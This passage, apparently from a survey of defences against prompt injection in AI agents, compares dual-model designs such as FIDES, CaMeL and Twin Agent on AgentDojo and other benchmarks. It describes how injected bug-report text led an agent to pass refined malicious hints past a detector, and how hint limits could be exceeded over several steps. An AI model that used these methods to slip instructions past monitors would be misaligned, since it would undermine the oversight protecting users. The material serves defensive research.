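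The choice of labels also favours the defence. Costa and colleagues marked a data field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it. The developer of a real system has no list of the fields attackers will use, and an attacker could inject instructions through a field wrongly marked as trusted.

The table gives the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack. The last row gives the share of tasks that are data-dependent, meaning that the right sequence of actions depends on what the agent finds. For example, booking a hotel only if its rating is above 4 is data-dependent, but sending the three latest emails to a colleague is not.

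| | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic agent, no policies | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o, basic agent with policies | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES with policies | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| o1, basic agent, no policies | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| o1, basic agent with policies | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| o1, FIDES with policies | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |
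| Share of data-dependent tasks | 5.0 | 10.0 | 43.8 | 42.9 |

With o1, the stronger of these two older models, protection reduced the completion rate by 5.5 percentage points in the workspace, 14 in travel, 40 in banking and 33 in Slack. These losses roughly follow the share of data-dependent tasks, in which the planner has to learn something from untrusted data before choosing its next action. A typed answer could supply that information.

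The tested version of FIDES left out constrained decoding, so the experiment can't show how many tasks typed answers would recover or whether one bit of influence is safe enough. The hotel booking policy, for example, required a trusted context and made no exception for an untrusted boolean.

About 20 of the 97 tasks are data-dependent, and typed answers would not recover all of them. A boolean is enough for the hotel booking, but several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which a fixed list can't cover unless the developer knows the possible instructions in advance. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) states more generally that two-model designs can't solve a task if the untrusted data specifies the necessary actions.

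Completion rates also include some lucky successes. One banking task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the transaction descriptions, but GPT-4o saw a large amount, decided it was suspicious and changed the password without reading the description. The benchmark counted this as a success.

### Counting the user's approvals

Kolluri and colleagues object to comparing a protected agent with one that can do anything without asking. Products such as OpenAI's Codex and GitHub Copilot ask the user to confirm consequential actions, so they rely on human attention for part of their security. Kolluri and colleagues therefore measured how many AgentDojo tasks an agent could complete without asking the user for approval.

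Separating the models makes an agent more useful, as measured by how much it can do without approval. With o3-mini, a basic agent that needed approval for every consequential action completed 24.3% of tasks on its own. FIDES, which needed approval only for actions that broke a policy, completed 50.1%. Prudentia, an extension of FIDES, completed 59.1% because its planner knows the policies and tries to avoid breaking them. The basic agent needed about 48 approvals for the tasks it completed, compared with about 19 for FIDES.

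Prudentia did even better on WASP, a benchmark for agents that browse the web. It blocked every attack without asking for approval. It also completed more tasks than the basic agent in seven of eight comparisons and the same number in the eighth, partly because injected text could no longer distract the planner. But the user's task was always to post a comment or upvote a post, and neither required the planner to read what other people had written.

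### Fixed attacks and newer models

Fixed attacks become less informative as models improve. *aiAuthZ* (2026) reports that two 2026 models resisted AgentDojo's standard banking attack in all 20 task-attack pairings, even without a defence. A list of approved payees therefore prevented no attacks in this test, but it blocked a legitimate payment to a new payee, which reduced the completion rate without an attack from 100% to 80%.

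The success rate of attacks on an undefended model also depends on what the attacker asks for. GPT-5.2 created the extra file in 98.9% of the bug-fixing cases, but followed almost none of the injected instructions in Choi and colleagues' tests. Bug reports normally ask for changes to the code, so a request for one more file may not look suspicious.

Usefulness is also hard to measure during an attack. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) shows that some AgentDojo attacks overwrite information the task needs. In one case, the user asks the agent to pay a bill, but the injection has replaced the payment details, so the agent can't complete the task even if it ignores the injected instructions.

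### Short hints in place of types

In *Twin Agent*, Hu, Jacob and colleagues (2026) criticise designs that pass only a restricted summary to the privileged model, including the typed agents that some of them had helped build. During a long task such as debugging, the information the privileged model needs changes along the way. A quarantined model that summarises a long report at the start has to select details before it is clear which ones will matter later. If a repair fails its tests, for example, the summary may omit the detail that explains why.

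Their alternative limits the length of a message instead of its type. An Explore Agent reads the untrusted text and follows the progress of a Safe Agent, which can use tools but can't read that text. At each step, the Explore Agent can send a short hint containing only what the Safe Agent needs next. The limit was 100 characters on two benchmarks and 200 on AgentDojo. In a separate check, a model blocks hints that look like injections.

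| Benchmark and model | Design | Tasks completed | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| 232 SWE-bench Lite cases, GPT-5.2 | Undefended | 61.2% | 97.0% |
| | Two models, nothing passed between them | 0% | 0% |
| | Twin Agent | 62.5% | 0% |
| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | Undefended | 61.9% | 41.5% |
| | CaMeL | 30.9% | 0% |
| | Twin Agent | 62.9% | 0.1% |
| DecodingTrust-Agent, GPT-5.2 | Undefended | 95.0% | 10.0% |
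| | Twin Agent | 95.0% | 3.3% |

Hu and colleagues selected 60 customer-management and finance tasks from DecodingTrust-Agent, another benchmark for agents with tools. On AgentDojo, the score on Slack tasks fell from 90.5% to 66.7%, but gains in the other settings offset this in the average. Hu and colleagues also cut CaMeL's maximum attempts from ten to three to save computing time, which lowered its completion rate below the roughly 35% reported in its original paper.

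Twin Agent appears to avoid the typed bug-fixing agent's loss of usefulness, but Hu and colleagues didn't compare the two directly. On SWE-bench, they compared Twin Agent with a design that passes no information from the bug report to the privileged model, and that design fixed no bugs. The tests in the two papers also used different selections of bug reports.

The protection is weaker in principle because a 100-character hint can contain an instruction. Hu and colleagues rely on the observation that successful injections against the strongest models tend to be long. To test this, they had an attacking model refine malicious hints over 100 rounds, then added text to each bug report telling the Explore Agent to copy one of these hints. In a separate test, the agent copied the hint every time.

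In complete runs, malicious hints got past the detector in 57 of 232 cases, and the Safe Agent carried out the attacker's order in 11 of those 57, an attack success rate of 4.7% across all 232 cases. When Hu and colleagues ran those 11 cases five more times each, no attack succeeded, which suggests the earlier successes were largely random. They accept that any success is still a security failure, and an attacker who can file many bug reports can keep trying.

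Hu and colleagues offer no formal guarantee and, because of the expense, did not test an attack that develops over several hints. An attacker who controls the Explore Agent could send up to 2,000 characters over 20 steps, so the limit on each hint doesn't keep the total short. In their tests, longer hints increased both usefulness and risk. At limits of 50 and 100 characters, Twin Agent cost about twice as much to run as the undefended agent.

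Hints are less necessary for the mailbox because its program needs only one answer about each email before filing it, and no new questions arise in later steps.

### Documents that need to be read together

A map call can't detect that two documents contradict each other because it processes only one. Code can often compare the outputs afterwards if the developer knows what to compare. To find the cheapest of 30 quotations, each map call can return a product number and a price, and code can sort the results. Code could also use these fields to detect that a supplier quoted €4.10 in one email and €4.60 in the next. This doesn't work for connections the developer didn't anticipate, such as an email that withdraws "the offer in my last message" without naming it.

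Existing systems often handle such tasks by letting one quarantined call read several documents. FIDES can give its quarantined model a list of variables, so a single question can cover three emails. Jacob and colleagues' calendar agent reads the whole thread for the same reason. In *SPA* (2026), a quarantined model without tools receives a question and one or more inputs, and is told to resolve references and implicit connections. The provider's API still forces its answer to fit a schema. These designs keep the protection of typed outputs but give up the isolation between documents, so any one document's author may be able to determine the joint answer.

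The mailbox program can avoid most of this risk by grouping emails by authenticated sender. If 40 suppliers send five emails each, the program can make 40 calls, and no supplier's text shares a context with another's. Checking every pair of emails would take 200 × 199 / 2 = 19,900 calls and would pair each supplier's text with every other supplier's. ReliabilityRAG looks for contradictions between the answers from isolated calls instead of between the documents. This exposes less text, but it misses contradictions that don't appear in the answers.

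Neither Jacob and colleagues nor Costa and colleagues compared separate calls with joint ones, so their results don't show how much isolation reduces accuracy. The company could estimate this by having the clerk mark which of 200 past emails make sense only alongside another. If there are only three, leaving such emails to the clerk would be easier than redesigning the program.

### The work of designing a schema

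A developer has to decide in advance what the acting step will need to know, which can take a lot of work even when the finished schema is short. Jacob and colleagues set aside 52 bug reports for development and needed considerable testing to settle on the fields for the bug-fixing agent. They list this work as a limitation and suggest that future research automate it.

FIDES saves some of this work by letting the planner write a schema for each question, but it requires other preparation. For the AgentDojo tests, Costa and colleagues assigned policies to 27 tools and wrote code to label the data those tools return. They also adjusted the planner's instructions by hand until it used variables properly. Hu and colleagues consider it an advantage that developers can add hints to an existing agent without designing a schema for each task, but the team still had to choose a length limit for each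 benchmark.

The mailbox's four categories are quick to write down but need maintenance. If suppliers start sending product recalls, the model will probably file them under "other", and every answer will still fit the schema. A rising share of emails under "other", or the clerk's random sample of those emails, can reveal that the schema needs a new category.

### Adoption

Companies seem to have been slow to adopt these designs in their agent products. A writer from the security company Sophos claims, in an SC Media article citing research from April 2026, that no mainstream agent product uses the dual-model pattern or CaMeL. The writer names Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI, and adds that CaMeL has no production-grade implementation. This is one practitioner's assessment, and companies don't always disclose how their agents work internally.

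The claim is consistent with Kolluri and colleagues' account of products that ask the user for confirmation. For example, Copilot Chat in Visual Studio Code can use read-only tools without asking, but needs the user's approval for others.

The Sophos writer attributes the difficulty to a conflict between safety and usefulness, and describes pilot projects that failed because the restrictions made the agents ineffective. The writer recommends measures that companies can add sooner. One is to run the agent in a sandbox that limits which files and networks it can reach. Another is to let the agent choose a tool and its parameters while a separate program holds the password and sends the request. These measures limit what a hijacked agent can do, but they don't keep untrusted text away from it.

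Research code is available for the stricter designs. Microsoft has published a tutorial for FIDES, and *L3M* describes a quarantined reader that developers can build from the system's components, although they don't have to use it.

The Sophos writer's claim is about general-purpose agents, so it is little guide to how many companies use map-reduce for a single task. A script that sends emails to a model one at a time and accepts only a category in return already has much of the structure described here. Its developer may have chosen it simply because it makes the results easy to count.
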